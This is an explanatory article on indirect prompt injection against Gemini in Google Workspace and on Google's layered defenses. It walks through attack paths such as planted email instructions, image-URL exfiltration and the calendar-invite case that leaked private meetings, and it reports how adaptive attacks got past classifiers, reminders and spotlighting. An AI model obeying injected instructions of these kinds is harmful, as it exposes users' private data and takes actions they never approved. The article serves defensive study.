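# Google's layered defenses against prompt injection for Gemini in Gmail, Docs and Workspace

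## How other people's text can give Gemini instructions

Workspace with Gemini is Google's AI assistant inside Gmail, Docs, Drive, Calendar and related apps. It summarizes email threads, drafts replies, finds facts in old messages and files, and creates calendar events. Most of these tasks require it to process text that the user did not write. Some of that text comes from colleagues, but anyone who knows the user's email address can send them a message, a shared file or a calendar invitation.

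Prompt injection exploits that openness. A prompt is the text that a large language model, the kind of AI model behind Gemini, receives and continues. In direct prompt injection, the attacker types malicious commands into the prompt. In indirect prompt injection, the attacker hides instructions in content that the system retrieves, such as an email, and the system follows them as if the user had given them. The attacker needs no password or access to the assistant, and the victim is the user, who has made an ordinary request and may never have opened the email.

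Google's *Mitigating prompt injection attacks with a layered defense strategy*, published on 13 June 2025, describes five defenses built into the product, in addition to training the model itself to resist such attacks. These defenses are easier to understand once it is clear why a model would obey a stranger's email.

### Why a model confuses data with instructions

Developers mostly solved a similar problem in older software. Databases take commands in a language called SQL, and attackers typed SQL into web forms to make the database run it. Parameterised queries prevent this by sending the command and the user's data separately, so the database can never interpret the data as a command.

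In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 article from the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, David C argues that language models have no equivalent of the parameterised queries that can eliminate SQL injection. A model receives a sequence of tokens (words or pieces of words) and calculates which token is likely to come next. The user's request and the stranger's email are both parts of that sequence. He thinks it very possible that prompt injection will never be eliminated in the way SQL injection can be. Google engineers Díaz, Kern and Olive (2025) describe the architecture in much the same way in *Google's Approach for Secure AI Agents*, writing that current models provide no "rigorous separation" between instructions and untrustworthy outside text.

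Developers mark the system instructions, the user's message and the output of tools with role tags, and train the model to give each a different authority. But the tags are only more input, and they compete with everything else in the text that hints at who is speaking. In *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026) built probes, small classifiers that estimate from a model's internal activations which role it has assigned to a piece of text. They trained the probes on identical web text wrapped in different tags, so that only the tags could account for a difference. When they put text that sounded like a user's inside a tool tag, the probes still gave it a 79 to 88 percent probability of being user text in three of the models they tested. On this account, a command in an email works because it sounds like it came from the user. Across 1,000 attempts to make an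 AI agent leak data, the attack success rate (the share of cases in which an injection achieves the attacker's goal) rose from 2 percent where the probes found the least role confusion to 70 percent where they found the most.

At least some models do register a difference internally between instructions and data, though. In *Readable Before Actionable*, Yu, Xing and colleagues (2026) gave two small open models the same sentence either as a request to carry out or as a note to summarize, with or without quotation marks. Their probe told the two roles apart with a score of about 0.92, where 0.5 is guessing and 1 is perfect, even after they reversed the link between quotation marks and role so that the punctuation would mislead it. A classifier that had only surface features such as length and position scored 0.51.

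Even when researchers can read the role signal inside a model, that signal evidently does not always determine what the model does next. In one of the two models, Qwen-2.5-7B, the researchers replaced the part of the internal state that lies along the role signal with the corresponding part from a prompt that called for a different tool. In the early and middle layers, this never changed which tool the model chose, though the role was already readable there. In later layers, it changed 82 to 98 percent of choices. The same research also used recorded attacks in which models followed injected commands.

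The two results probably conflict less than they seem. Yu and colleagues used honestly framed notes that did not imitate anyone, while Ye and colleagues specifically tested imitation. Neither group's probe results are for Gemini, so the percentages can't be assumed to apply to it. Both groups agree that the separation is missing, however, and Google concedes this for current models in general.

### From request to answer

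In this invented example, a user asks Gemini in Gmail to summarize 20 unread emails. Nineteen are harmless, but one from a stranger contains a passage addressed to Gemini below some ordinary sentences. The email passes through the stages that Google describes.

Gemini first retrieves material for the request. *The life of a prompt* (Chilakapati and Camery, 2024), Google's account for business customers, stresses that Gemini retrieves only relevant content that the user has permission to see. This protects against one employee reading another's files, but it doesn't keep out the stranger's email, which is in the user's own inbox. The spam filter might have kept it out, because Gemini has no access to content that Google has already identified as malicious, such as spam, according to Google's *Privacy, Security, Data Governance, & Compliance White Paper* (2025), but this email got past that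 filter.

Gemini can also read messages the user didn't point it to. By May 2026, Google was describing a retrieval engine, Workspace Intelligence, that searches Gmail, Drive, Calendar and Chat for context on a request. If a user asks about next week's schedule, the engine can retrieve an invitation from a stranger.

Next, software assembles the prompt by joining Google's system instructions, the user's question and the 20 emails. It may also add stored information from earlier conversations. The stranger's words and the user's words are now in one sequence.

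The model then either answers or first makes a tool call, which is a request to run a function. According to Google's help page *Collaborate with Gemini in Gmail*, Gemini can find information in earlier emails and Drive files, look up calendar events and create new ones, which implies that it has such functions. In the general design that Díaz and colleagues describe, the agent runs a tool with authority from the user, and the result can feed into another round of planning. They warn that every round gives malicious data another chance to take over.

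Finally, the app displays the answer, which can contain links and images as well as text. Fetching an image from an outside server sends that server the image's web address, including any private data the address contains.

### Three kinds of harm

If Gemini follows instructions in a stranger's text, what happens next depends on the attacker's aim. The defenses differ greatly in which aims they can block.

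An attacker's simplest aim is to make Gemini give a misleading answer. A summary might include a false claim that a meeting has moved or that an account needs urgent attention, and the user may believe it because they trust the assistant. The attack doesn't send out data or run a function; the harm comes when the user acts on the answer. *New Gemini for Workspace Vulnerability*, by the security company HiddenLayer, includes phishing through Gemini in Gmail among its examples.

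A separate risk is exfiltration, which means moving private data to a place where the attacker can read it. An injection might cause Gemini to look up something confidential and put it in a link or an image address. Gemini might also use a tool that sends information out, so a leak can involve an action too.

The third harm is an unauthorized action, in which Gemini makes a change the user never asked for, such as deleting a calendar event. The possible damage depends on the tools Gemini can use. David C advises designers to assume the worst that an attacker could do with direct access to those tools. With a wide enough set of tools, the effects can be physical. Ye and colleagues cite a 2025 study by Nassi and others in which an emailed invitation was enough to turn on a boiler.

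Díaz and colleagues use two categories, "rogue actions" and "sensitive data disclosure", which fit the last two harms well. A false summary fits them less well because it may involve neither a tool nor sensitive data. It is worth treating separately because, as the example shows, fewer of Google's defenses apply to it.

### Where the five defenses act

Google lists five defenses in this order: content classifiers, security thought reinforcement, markdown sanitization with URL redaction, user confirmation, and security notices. They act at different points on the path of the 20 emails.

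A content classifier is a separate machine-learning model that judges whether retrieved content contains malicious instructions. It examines the emails before Gemini summarizes them. If it detects that one of twenty emails is malicious, Gemini leaves that email out and summarizes the other nineteen. Google describes this outcome to Workspace administrators, but it warns ordinary users that one malicious message may mean they get no summary at all.

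If the classifier misses the email, all 20 go into the prompt. At this stage, security thought reinforcement adds instructions around the prompt content that tell the model to do the user's task and ignore commands in the content. These instructions are also text in the prompt, so they make the model less likely to follow the stranger's commands but can't guarantee that it won't.

Model hardening, which Google counts separately from the five layers, means training Gemini itself to recognize and ignore injected instructions. According to Google DeepMind's *Advancing Gemini's security safeguards* (2025), an automated system attacked Gemini in realistic scenarios and produced effective injections that targeted sensitive information. The company then fine-tuned Gemini (trained it further) on those scenarios to carry out the user's original request and disregard the planted one. Google DeepMind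 reports a lower attack success rate with no significant loss on normal tasks, but adds that "no model is completely immune". The white paper *Lessons from Defending Gemini Against Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) gives the technical details.

If all of these defenses fail and the model follows the email's instructions, user confirmation may still stop an unauthorized action, because the assistant must get the user's explicit approval for certain risky operations. A user who asked for a summary and now sees a request to delete Saturday's appointments can refuse. If the attacker wanted data, two more defenses apply when the answer is displayed. Models write links and images in a simple formatting code called Markdown, and Markdown sanitization removes or refuses to display risky elements, especially external images. URL redaction replaces a link judged suspicious with a notice that it was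 removed.

If the attacker only wants to put a false sentence in the summary, these later checks don't help, because there is no function to approve and no image or link to remove. The only remaining defenses are the classifier, the reminder and the hardened model, each of which has to interpret language and can make mistakes.

The remaining defense is the security notice, which tells the user that Gemini found suspicious content and removed or limited its answer. In the example, it would appear above the summary of nineteen emails and explain that Gemini had excluded some content. The notice appears only if another defense detects the injection. Otherwise, the user sees what looks like a normal answer.

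### What Google has made public

The June 2025 post announcing the five defenses is the fullest public description of them as a set, but it does not evaluate them. It uses "Gemini" for both Workspace with Gemini and the Gemini app, Google's standalone chatbot. Its illustrations show a redacted link in Gmail, a confirmation request in the Gemini app and a security notice in Docs. An outsider cannot tell from the post whether every defense was running in every product.

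The timing is also unclear. Google wrote that it was still "in the process of rolling out" the content classifiers. But its Workspace white paper from two months earlier, which expressly excludes the Gemini app, had already listed detecting malicious instructions in files, emails and attachments among Workspace's protections. Perhaps the new classifiers replaced older ones, or extended them to more formats. By May 2026 the company's privacy pages described threat checks as a routine step before Gemini performs an action, so the rollout had presumably progressed.

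The larger gap is that the post gives no attack success rate for any of the five defenses or for the combination, and no false positive rate (the share of harmless items that a detector wrongly flags). The April 2025 white paper reports from "early analysis" that the layers detect and mitigate "the majority" of prompt injection attacks, which could mean 55 percent or 99 percent. *Google Workspace's continuous approach to mitigating indirect prompt injections* (Gavish, 2026) explains how Google updates the defenses and measures each change, but it doesn't give attack success rates either.

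In the post's paragraph on content classifiers, Google says that Gmail automatically blocks more than 99.9 percent of spam, phishing attempts and malware. The same claim appears on Gmail's product page, *Email that keeps your private information safe*, where it is plainly about what reaches the inbox. It is not a detection rate for prompt injection. An email can carry instructions for an assistant without advertising anything, asking for a password or attaching a virus, and the twentieth email in the example had already passed Gmail's filter before Gemini retrieved it.

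## Classifiers that screen emails and files

Content classifiers are the first of the five defenses and the only one that can keep an injection out of the prompt entirely. They are separate from Gemini, so Google can retrain them on a new attack without retraining Gemini. A classifier also has no tools and writes nothing to the user, so an attacker who fools it only gets the injection into the prompt. The drawback is that a classifier must judge the text before anyone knows what Gemini would do with it.

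### What happens after the verdict

According to Google, if the classifier finds malicious instructions in every email or file used for a request, Gemini gives no answer. If it finds them in only some, Gemini drops those items and answers from the rest. If it finds none, Gemini answers as usual. Google tells Workspace administrators that the check on files looks for suspicious links as well as suspicious prompts. Gemini also blocks the answer when the conversation itself contains an attempted injection. Google's *How Gemini Apps help protect users from malicious content & prompt injection* describes the same total and partial exclusions for the standalone Gemini app.

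As described, Gemini drops a whole email or a whole file. That works well for an inbox summary, where losing one email in twenty matters little. It works less well for a single long document, where one planted paragraph leaves the user with no answer at all, as in Google's illustration of a security notice in Docs. It probably also means that anyone who can write in a shared document can stop Gemini from summarizing it by pasting in something that looks like an attack. This is only a nuisance, since nothing leaks, and any filter that fails closed has the same problem.

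In Google's diagrams, content that passes the classifiers moves on to the security reminders, where Gemini can still block the response.

### Learning from reported attacks

Google trained the classifiers on a catalog of AI vulnerabilities and adversarial data, which it built with outside researchers through its AI Vulnerability Reward Program. The program pays people who privately report flaws in Google's AI products. Google says the models draw on real-world examples and cover "various formats, such as emails and files". It does not give the catalog's size or describe the models' design.

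Training data of this kind is valuable because it comes from people who were seriously trying to break the product. Examples invented by a company might easily be cruder than real injections, or all alike. But the catalog contains only attacks that someone has found and chosen to report. A classifier trained on it learns the features those attacks share, which a new attack may lack. Text that openly addresses an AI assistant and tells it to disregard its user should be easy to learn to detect, but a polite request that could have come from the user is much harder because the catalog's examples of such requests resemble a lot of ordinary mail.

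Google responds by continuing to add to the data, and Gavish describes retraining that includes synthetic attacks. The production classifiers have no published detection rate, so the closest measurements of how well this works come from a different set of detectors.

### DeepMind's experiments with stand-ins

*Lessons from Defending Gemini Against Indirect Prompt Injections*, a May 2025 report from Google DeepMind, tested several defenses on Gemini 2.0, the generation before the 2.5 models in Google's June post. In the experiment, a user gives Gemini a calendar task that requires it to retrieve data an attacker has tampered with. The attacker wants the user's passport number, and the attack succeeds if Gemini reveals it.

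The researchers generated all the injections with three automated attacks, which are programs that produce a candidate injection, test it, and use the result to search for a better one. In the non-adaptive runs, the programs developed their injections without the defense in place, and the researchers then tried the finished injections on the defended system. In the adaptive runs, the defense was in place from the start, so the programs could search for injections that got past it.

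Two of the defenses were classifiers, and they differed in what they received as input:

- The retrieved-data classifier reads the content that Gemini has fetched and judges whether it contains an injection. This is the same position that Google's production classifiers occupy.
- The user-instruction classifier never receives the fetched content. It gets the user's request and the model's response, and judges whether the one fits the other.

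Neither was a production classifier. The researchers based both on ShieldGemma, Google's openly available family of safety classifiers, designed to catch content such as harassment and dangerous material. They told the model what to look for in a written prompt and did not fine-tune it on injections, whereas Google's production models had a catalog of injections to learn from. The percentages below are therefore some evidence about where to put a detector, but very little evidence about how many attacks get past the one in Gmail.

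| Defense and type of run | Attack 1 | Attack 2 | Attack 3 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Retrieved-data classifier, non-adaptive | 68.2% | 0.4% | 37.6% |
| Retrieved-data classifier, adaptive | 5.0% | 14.8% | 10.8% |
| User-instruction classifier, adaptive | 0% | 0.4% | 3.0% |

*Attack success rates on Gemini 2.0; lower is better for the defender.*

In the top two rows, two of the three attacks did far worse when they could adapt to the defense, even though practicing against a defense should help an attacker. The most likely explanation is how the attack programs search. They improve an injection in small steps, and each step needs some sign that the last one helped. When a classifier rejects nearly every early attempt, the programs get no such sign. A program that practices on undefended Gemini does get this feedback and arrives at a strong injection, which quite often gets past the classifier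 anyway.

If that is right, the adaptive figures make the retrieved-data classifier look more effective than it was. An attacker who has prepared a good injection without the defense can just send it, so the higher of the two figures for each attack (68.2, 14.8 and 37.6 percent) is the better guide to the risk. By that measure, this stand-in was a weak defense. A determined human might do even better, since a person can guess why a classifier flagged the text and rewrite it without needing a gradually rising score as a guide.

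A better search might also find more in the bottom row, so the same caution applies there. But the user-instruction classifier had the lower rate on all three attacks under the same adaptive conditions, as there is good reason to expect.

### Why it helps to hide the email from the detector

The retrieved-data classifier has the same weakness as the model it protects, because it is also a language model that reads text written by the attacker. The attacker has to write one passage that the classifier labels harmless and Gemini follows as a command. This is difficult, but the attacker controls every word the classifier reads and can even aim the passage at the classifier itself.

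Nicolas Lidzborski, a security engineer for Google Workspace, made the same criticism in a March 2026 talk. The published notes, *Securing Workspace GenAI at Google*, list machine-learning classifiers among the defenses that fail in a "cat-and-mouse" game with attackers. They call using a language model as judge a "recursive trap", presumably because the judge can be manipulated in the same way as the model it judges. The notes also mention multimodal blind spots, where a text filter misses attacks contained in images or other media. Lidzborski also argued for defense in depth, so his objection is to relying on classifiers alone.

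The user-instruction classifier mostly avoids this problem because the email is not part of its input. An attacker can influence that input only through Gemini's response, which must contain the theft for the attack to succeed. If a user asks for help with a calendar and the response sends a passport number to a stranger, the request and response don't match, however the email is worded.

The classifier works poorly when the user's request is vague. If a user writes "go through my inbox and deal with whatever needs doing", the right response might include sending someone a document, accepting an invitation or creating three events, depending on what the emails say. The classifier can't read the emails, so it must either allow almost any action or block a good deal of legitimate work. This is a problem because people make open-ended requests when they trust an assistant to act alone, which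 is also when an injection can do the most damage.

Misleading answers are a second gap. If the user asks for a summary and gets one containing a false sentence, the response still matches the request. Only a detector that reads the email has a chance of noticing where the false sentence came from.

The two designs also differ in what the product can do after an alarm. A classifier that checks each email separately can identify the bad one, so Gemini can leave it out and summarize the other nineteen. A classifier that compares the request with the response can detect a problem but can't identify which email caused it, so the system can do little except block the response or start again with less material.

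A company can use both, but Google's public description covers only classifiers that screen content, so it would be a mistake to credit Workspace with the low figures in the bottom row of the table.

### False alarms

A classifier can stop every attack by flagging every email it reads, so an attack success rate means little without a false positive rate.

The DeepMind researchers measured the retrieved-data classifier's false positives on spam emails that contained no injections, using the older Gemini 1.5 models. The classifier wrongly flagged 82.1 percent of the emails with Gemini 1.5 Flash, the smaller and faster model, and 31.1 percent with Gemini 1.5 Pro. The researchers attributed these errors to the makeshift detector, which used a prompt and had no fine-tuning for the task.

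Spam is also about the hardest harmless text to test a detector on. It is full of commands (click here, reply today, confirm your details), and a detector that has only a general description of "malicious instructions" will flag many of them. An injection differs in that its commands are meant for the assistant rather than the person. A prompt can state that distinction, but thousands of labeled examples would probably teach it better, so the production classifiers should do much better than 31 percent. They would need to, because if ordinary mail were flagged as often as the spam was, Gemini would leave out six of the twenty emails in the earlier example at the Pro rate and sixteen at the Flash rate.

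These figures also can't be combined with the attack success rates in the table, which come from Gemini 2.0. The false positive rate comes from a different generation of model, so it doesn't show how many harmless emails the classifier flagged while it held the three adaptive attacks to success rates between 5 and 15 percent.

Because nearly all email is harmless, even a classifier far better than the stand-in can flag many more harmless emails than malicious ones. In a hypothetical example, Gemini reads a million emails for the staff of a large company, one email in 100,000 contains an injection, and the classifier has a false positive rate of 1 percent. Ten of the emails are then malicious, and the classifier wrongly flags about 10,000 of the 999,990 harmless ones. Even if it also catches all 10 attacks, only about one in a thousand flagged emails contains an injection.

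Write *p* for the share of emails that are malicious, *d* for the share of malicious emails that the classifier catches, and *f* for the false positive rate. The share of flags that are correct is then

*pd* / (*pd* + (1 − *p*)*f*).

When *p* is tiny, the share of flags that are correct depends almost entirely on how *f* compares with *p*. For half of all flags to be correct, *f* must fall to about *p*, which here is one false alarm in 100,000 harmless emails, or a thousandth of the 1 percent rate. Raising *d* from 90 to 100 percent hardly changes the share because it adds only one correct flag per million emails, although that email may matter a lot to the person who received it.

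If the errors are independent, someone who asks for a summary of 20 emails every working day would lose at least one harmless email from about 18 percent of the summaries, or nearly one summary a week. The same person would receive a real injection about once in 20 years. Most people would conclude well before then that the warnings are meaningless, and a missing email might be an important one, such as a message from a school or bank.

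The value of *p* varies from person to person because attackers pick their targets. For a finance director in the middle of an acquisition, one email in a thousand might be an attack. A 1 percent false positive rate would then produce about ten false alarms for each real attack, which is annoying but tolerable. A company could sensibly run a stricter classifier for such people, if the product allowed it.

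Classifiers typically produce a score, and the developer chooses the threshold above which the system acts. A higher threshold means fewer false alarms but more missed attacks. Google hasn't published its threshold, but it probably chose a high one, because even a low false alarm rate would affect many messages in a mass-market product, and the four defenses behind the classifier can catch some of the attacks it misses. Google does expect some mistakes, and advises administrators that users should send feedback when they think Gemini has wrongly identified a threat. Those reports could help retrain the classifier, since they are examples of harmless mail that it gets wrong.

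A detector that Google has tuned to leave ordinary mail alone will have the most trouble with an attack that resembles ordinary mail.

### A calendar invitation that got through

The security company Miggo found an attack of that kind. Miggo's *Weaponizing Calendar Invites* describes an invitation whose description field contained instructions for Gemini. The target didn't have to open the invitation. When they asked Gemini an everyday question about their schedule, Gemini loaded the relevant events, including the attacker's.

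Gemini then summarized the target's meetings for a particular day, including private ones, and wrote the summary into a new calendar event. Its short reply to the user gave no hint of this. Whether the attacker could read the new event depended on the organization's calendar settings. Miggo says it was visible in many enterprise configurations, while SiliconANGLE's *Indirect prompt injection in Google Gemini enabled unauthorized access to meeting data* (2026), which covered the findings on 19 January, says "some". Where the event was visible, the data leaked entirely within Google's own calendar system, without any link or image.

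According to Miggo, the attack worked even though Google had already deployed a separate language model to detect malicious prompts. Miggo attributes this to the instructions being plausible as user requests, since people do ask assistants to summarize their meetings and create events. The text was harmful only because a stranger had written it and the assistant had access to both the victim's private calendar and a tool that could write to a place the stranger could see.

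Miggo concludes that defenders "must evolve beyond keyword blocking". That is true but doesn't quite address the problem, since a language model trained to detect injections doesn't block keywords. Such a model can understand the sentence and still pass it, because the sentence is harmless if the user wrote it. The classifier needed to consider who the author was. An event description from an outsider has little reason to give an assistant instructions, and a classifier that flagged every instruction addressed to an assistant, malicious or not, would have had a much better chance of catching this attack. It would also have flagged more harmless mail, because colleagues write things like "please add this to your calendar and send me a summary", and it isn't always clear whether they mean the person or the software.

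A user-instruction check might have done well, because the user asked whether a day was free and Gemini created an event full of meeting details. But the check would have needed to cover tool calls as well as the reply shown on screen. The reply answered the user's question, so a classifier that compared only the two would have found nothing wrong.

Miggo tested from outside Google, so it could see that the attack succeeded but not what Google's detector did. The detector may have scanned the invitation and classified it as harmless, as Miggo believes, or it may not have covered event descriptions at the time. Google's June 2025 post says injections can arrive in calendar invitations, but its description of the classifiers gives only emails and files as examples.

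The timing is consistent with that second possibility. Miggo's published example shows meetings on Saturday 19 July, which matches the 2025 calendar. The tests therefore probably took place in the summer of 2025, within weeks of Google's announcement that it was still rolling out the classifiers. The case is good evidence that a plausible request could get past Google's defenses at that time, but weaker evidence about the classifiers Google was running when the findings were published the following January.

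Miggo says Google confirmed and mitigated the vulnerability, and SecurityWeek's *Weaponized Invite Enabled Calendar Data Theft via Google Gemini* also reports that Google addressed it. None of the accounts describes the fix. Google could have retrained the classifier on attacks of this type, though a differently worded attack might still get past it. It could also have restricted when Gemini may create an event after reading a stranger's text, which would apply however the request was worded.

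## Security reminders added to the prompt

Some injections look like ordinary mail and will get past almost any classifier, as Miggo's invitation apparently did. Google's next defense, which it calls security thought reinforcement, applies to text that has already reached the prompt. Google describes it as "targeted security instructions surrounding the prompt content" that remind the model to do the user's task and ignore adversarial instructions. Google has not published the instructions, but "surrounding" suggests that some come before the retrieved content and some after it.

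According to the description of Google's diagram, after the classifiers have passed the content, "an additional reasoning step" determines whether Gemini blocks the final response. The main text does not explain this step. A reminder is only text, so it can't block a response itself. Perhaps it leads Gemini to consider, as it reasons before answering, whether the emails contain an attack, and Gemini declines to answer if it finds one. The name "thought reinforcement" fits that reading.

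Gemini might instead run a separate check on its draft answer. In *Lessons from Defending Gemini Against Indirect Prompt Injections*, DeepMind researchers tried this kind of check, called self-reflection, by asking Gemini 2.0 whether it was looking at a prompt injection. Their three adaptive attacks still succeeded 54.6, 66.2 and 26.0 percent of the time. If Google's extra step works like this, it is probably not a strong barrier.

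### How reminders differ from the other defenses

Unlike a classifier, which removes the emails it flags, a security reminder leaves all 20 emails from the earlier example in the prompt, so the user never loses a harmless one. Any harm to ordinary use would come from worse answers.

Google can rewrite a reminder without retraining the model, which model hardening requires. But DeepMind also used warnings in the prompt to harden Gemini 2.5. To make training examples, it took injections that had worked, added a warning to the prompt, and kept the responses in which Gemini then ignored the injection. It trained the new model to respond the same way, in effect teaching it to act as if the warning were there.

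Spotlighting marks untrusted text so the model can tell where it is. The original 2024 version, by Hines and others, replaced the spaces between the words of that text with a warning word. DeepMind's version inserts a special token after every eight characters of an email's sender, subject and body, and adds an instruction not to trust marked text. Google doesn't mention this kind of marking in its post.

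The researchers found, unexpectedly, that spotlighting worked mainly by breaking up the words of the injection, which made the model less likely to treat them as a command but still let it summarize the email. They therefore expect it to work poorly in Chinese or Japanese, where a single character can carry the meaning of a word. A plain reminder leaves the text intact, so it works only if the model understands and follows it.

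### Why a reminder helps but guarantees nothing

Developers train models to follow instructions, and a reminder is an instruction. Without one, the prompt may contain a short, vague request from the user and a long, insistent command in an email. The reminder gives the user's request some support. If Ye and colleagues are right that models identify the source of text partly from its style, the reminder also helps by stating directly which text came from outside. It adds little to the prompt's length, since DeepMind's basic description of prompt injection took 88 tokens, far fewer than 20 emails would.

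The same model reads the reminder and the injection as text in one sequence, and no separate program checks whether the model followed the reminder. An attacker can also guess that the prompt includes a reminder and write the injection to account for it.

An injection doesn't have to contradict the reminder. In *The Attacker Moves Second*, Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025) tested prompt sandwiching, a defense that repeats the user's request after the untrusted text so that the model doesn't lose track of it. One common technique got past this defense by presenting the malicious task as something the user's own task required. Repeating the request doesn't prevent this, because the injected text makes the malicious task look like part of what the user asked for.

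Spotlighting and sandwiching both had attack success rates as low as 1 percent against the ready-made attacks in AgentDojo, a simulated environment for testing AI agents. An adaptive search then raised the rate above 95 percent for both. In a contest with more than 500 participants, people found 265 successful attacks against spotlighting and 178 against sandwiching. Nasr and colleagues saw no measurable difference between the kinds of attack that worked with these defenses and without them.

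### DeepMind's tests on Gemini 2.0

DeepMind tested three prompt-level defenses on the calendar task from the classifier experiments, in which the attacker wants the user's passport number. The first was an explanation of prompt injection, with examples, placed before the retrieved content. The second was spotlighting. The third was a warning at the end of the prompt, after the retrieved content, telling Gemini not to expose the user's private information.

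| Defense | Attack 1 | Attack 2 | Attack 3 |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 96.8% | 98.6% | 100% |
| Explanation with examples, before the content | 46.2% → 59.8% | 34.4% → 66.6% | 67.6% → 98.4% |
| Spotlighting | 18.0% → 82.4% | 13.0% → 64.8% | 75.2% → 82.2% |
| Warning, after the content | 5.8% → 8.4% | 0.2% → 0% | 1.2% → 10.8% |

*Attack success rates on Gemini 2.0. Where there is an arrow, the figure before it is for injections prepared without the defense and the figure after it is for adaptive attacks.*

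Spotlighting stopped more than four in five ready-made injections from Attacks 1 and 2. Once the attacks could adapt, it stopped only 17.6 percent of attempts with Attack 1 and 35.2 percent with Attack 2.

Adapting the attacks to this defense raised their success rate in eight of the nine pairs, unlike with the retrieved-data classifier. This is probably because a reminder seldom blocks an attack completely, so the search has partial successes to build on.

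The warning worked much better than the other two. It also beat the retrieved-data classifier on all three attacks when compared using the higher of the two rates for each attack. That is striking for a little extra text, even though the classifier was makeshift.

An attack success rate of 10.8 percent is still high for a security measure. The researchers scored each attack by its best single injection, tested on conversations the attack had not seen, so one fixed text extracted the passport number from roughly one conversation in nine. That would be enough for an attacker who can send the same email to thousands of people, if no other defense stopped the attack. Attack 3 found its best injection with 1,080 queries to Gemini, compared with 4,320 without a defense, so the warning made the attack less effective but did not make the search longer.

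### Where the reminder goes

The DeepMind researchers attribute the gap between the warning and the explanation mainly to position. The table can't prove this, because the two texts also differ in content, with one describing a type of attack and the other forbidding a specific act. An earlier experiment on Gemini 1.5 Flash is better evidence because it moved the same description from one place to another. That experiment used an email task and injections from Attack 1.

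With no defense, the attack succeeded 98.4 percent of the time. Describing prompt injection in the system instructions, before the email, lowered the rate only to 98.2 percent, but putting the description after the email lowered it to 63.4 percent. A single example of the right response, also after the email, brought it down to 19.8 percent. Examples placed before the email helped much less, leaving the rate at 89.6 percent with two examples and 91.6 percent with eight.

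A reminder at the start of the prompt is probably too far from the model's answer to work well, because the attacker's text comes in between. Placing the reminder at the end puts it after that text, just before the answer.

Security reminders can also make Gemini's answers worse. DeepMind had an automated grader score Gemini's summaries of harmless emails. Examples in the system instructions barely changed the score (0.287 without them, 0.283 with them), but reminders after the email lowered it from 0.29 to 0.20 and, at worst, 0.12. That is a serious drawback because it affects every user's summaries, and very few summaries involve an attack. However, the harmless emails were spam, which may be especially likely to make a model overcautious right after a warning. DeepMind didn't include the short warning in these measurements, so it may lower the quality of summaries less than the examples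 did.

Putting text after the untrusted content isn't enough by itself, either. Sandwiching, which repeats the user's request there, failed against more than 95 percent of the adaptive attacks that Nasr and colleagues ran. They used a different benchmark and searched for attacks differently, so the comparison with DeepMind's warning is rough. But it makes sense that forbidding a specific harm would work better than repeating the request.

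Reminders can also be less effective when documents are longer. *MINE* (2026) tested several prompt-level defenses on Llama-3.1-70B, an older open model, using questions about documents that contained two planted passages. With a reminder, 61.1 percent of attacks got through, rising to more than 97 percent with longer documents. With sandwiching, fewer attacks got through, but the rate still rose from 16.3 to 39.8 percent. The researchers had designed the attack to get past their own filter, not reminders, so an attack aimed at reminders could succeed more often. The trend is worrying for Workspace, where long email threads and files are normal.

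### Two reasons to discount the warning's score

The warning forbade Gemini to reveal private information, but users sometimes want it to, such as when they ask it to send their passport number to a travel agent. The DeepMind researchers note that this could make such a warning difficult to use in a real product.

The warning also prohibited exactly what the test measured, which was revealing private data. Google's reminder, as described, is more general and tells the model to do the user's task and ignore commands in the content. That wording allows the email to the travel agent. It should also cover commands to delete an appointment or add a false sentence to a summary, which a ban on revealing private data would not. But a general instruction leaves the model more to interpret, so there is no good reason to expect it to match the warning's results of 8.4, 0 and 10.8 percent.

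The researchers also caution that the warning is probably overfitted to a simple setting. In their tests, the attacker needed Gemini to make one extra tool call immediately after reading the injection. A real assistant may read an email, search Drive, read a file and then write a reply. Each step adds new text, so a reminder placed at the end of the prompt is soon in the middle. The developer can repeat the reminder after every step, but DeepMind's experiment doesn't show how well that works over a long task.

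For both reasons, the warning is better seen as one part of a larger defense. DeepMind later combined it with the hardened Gemini 2.5, and the combination worked better than either alone.

### Newer models

Gemini 2.0 is now several generations old, and results from one generation have not carried over well to the next. With spotlighting, only 0 to 3 percent of ready-made attacks succeeded against Gemini 1.5 Flash, partly because the model often returned an empty answer. With the same defense, up to 75 percent succeeded against Gemini 2.0, though on a different task.

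In *Scaling Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks with Agent Swarms*, Kurakin, Karande and colleagues (2026) attacked four recent Gemini models with Google's defenses outside the model switched off. Their attacker was a group of AI agents that shared notes and had up to 320 attempts at each task. It found a working injection for 99 percent of the tasks with Gemini 3.6 Flash and 34 percent with Gemini 4 Argon. These figures aren't comparable with the 2025 ones, because the agents could write a new injection for each task and the goal was a harmless but unrelated tool call. They give a baseline for a security reminder to improve on, but Kurakin and colleagues did not test one.

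In *AutoDojo*, Ma, Li and colleagues (2026) tested security reminders on five models from several companies. Before each piece of retrieved content, they inserted a sentence telling the agent not to execute any instruction in it. Their version of spotlighting put markers around the content. They ran a ready-made attack and an adaptive one. The table gives the higher of the two success rates, since a real attacker could use either.

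| Model | No defense | Reminder | Spotlighting |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o-mini | 58.6% | 40.4% | 51.7% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | 50.4% | 45.0% | 54.5% |
| DeepSeek-v4-Flash | 22.6% | 5.9% | 13.9% |
| GPT-5.4-mini | 8.7% | 2.1% | 5.4% |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 1.8% | 1.0% | 1.8% |

*Attack success rates across three groups of AgentDojo tasks.*

The reminder cut the rate by about three quarters on DeepSeek-v4-Flash and GPT-5.4-mini, even though it came before the content. It hardly affected the share of ordinary tasks that the agents completed, so a single sentence seems to avoid most of the loss of usefulness that DeepMind found with examples. The reminder did very little on Gemini 2.5 Flash, the only Google model of the five, and didn't help it at all on a second set of tasks, where the rate was 52.0 percent without the reminder and 53.6 percent with it. Ma and colleagues left out AgentDojo's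 own workspace tasks because the long documents caused too many failures even without an attack, so the results don't cover the kind of work closest to Gmail and Docs.

The low rates in the bottom rows may also be partly due to weak attacks, since the adaptive search had only six rounds for each target. *AgentDyn* (2026) reports that adaptive attacks on GPT-5-mini, GPT-5.1 and Claude Sonnet 4.5 succeeded in only 2.1 to 5.6 percent of cases, and concludes that attack methods were lagging behind defenses. But in the 500-round campaigns described in *Evaluation of Prompt Injection Defenses in Large Language Models* (2026), the strongest defenses that relied on the model held for 247 to 277 rounds and then failed almost completely. Those were direct injections, where the attacker talks to the model, but someone preparing a malicious email could practice on their own account.

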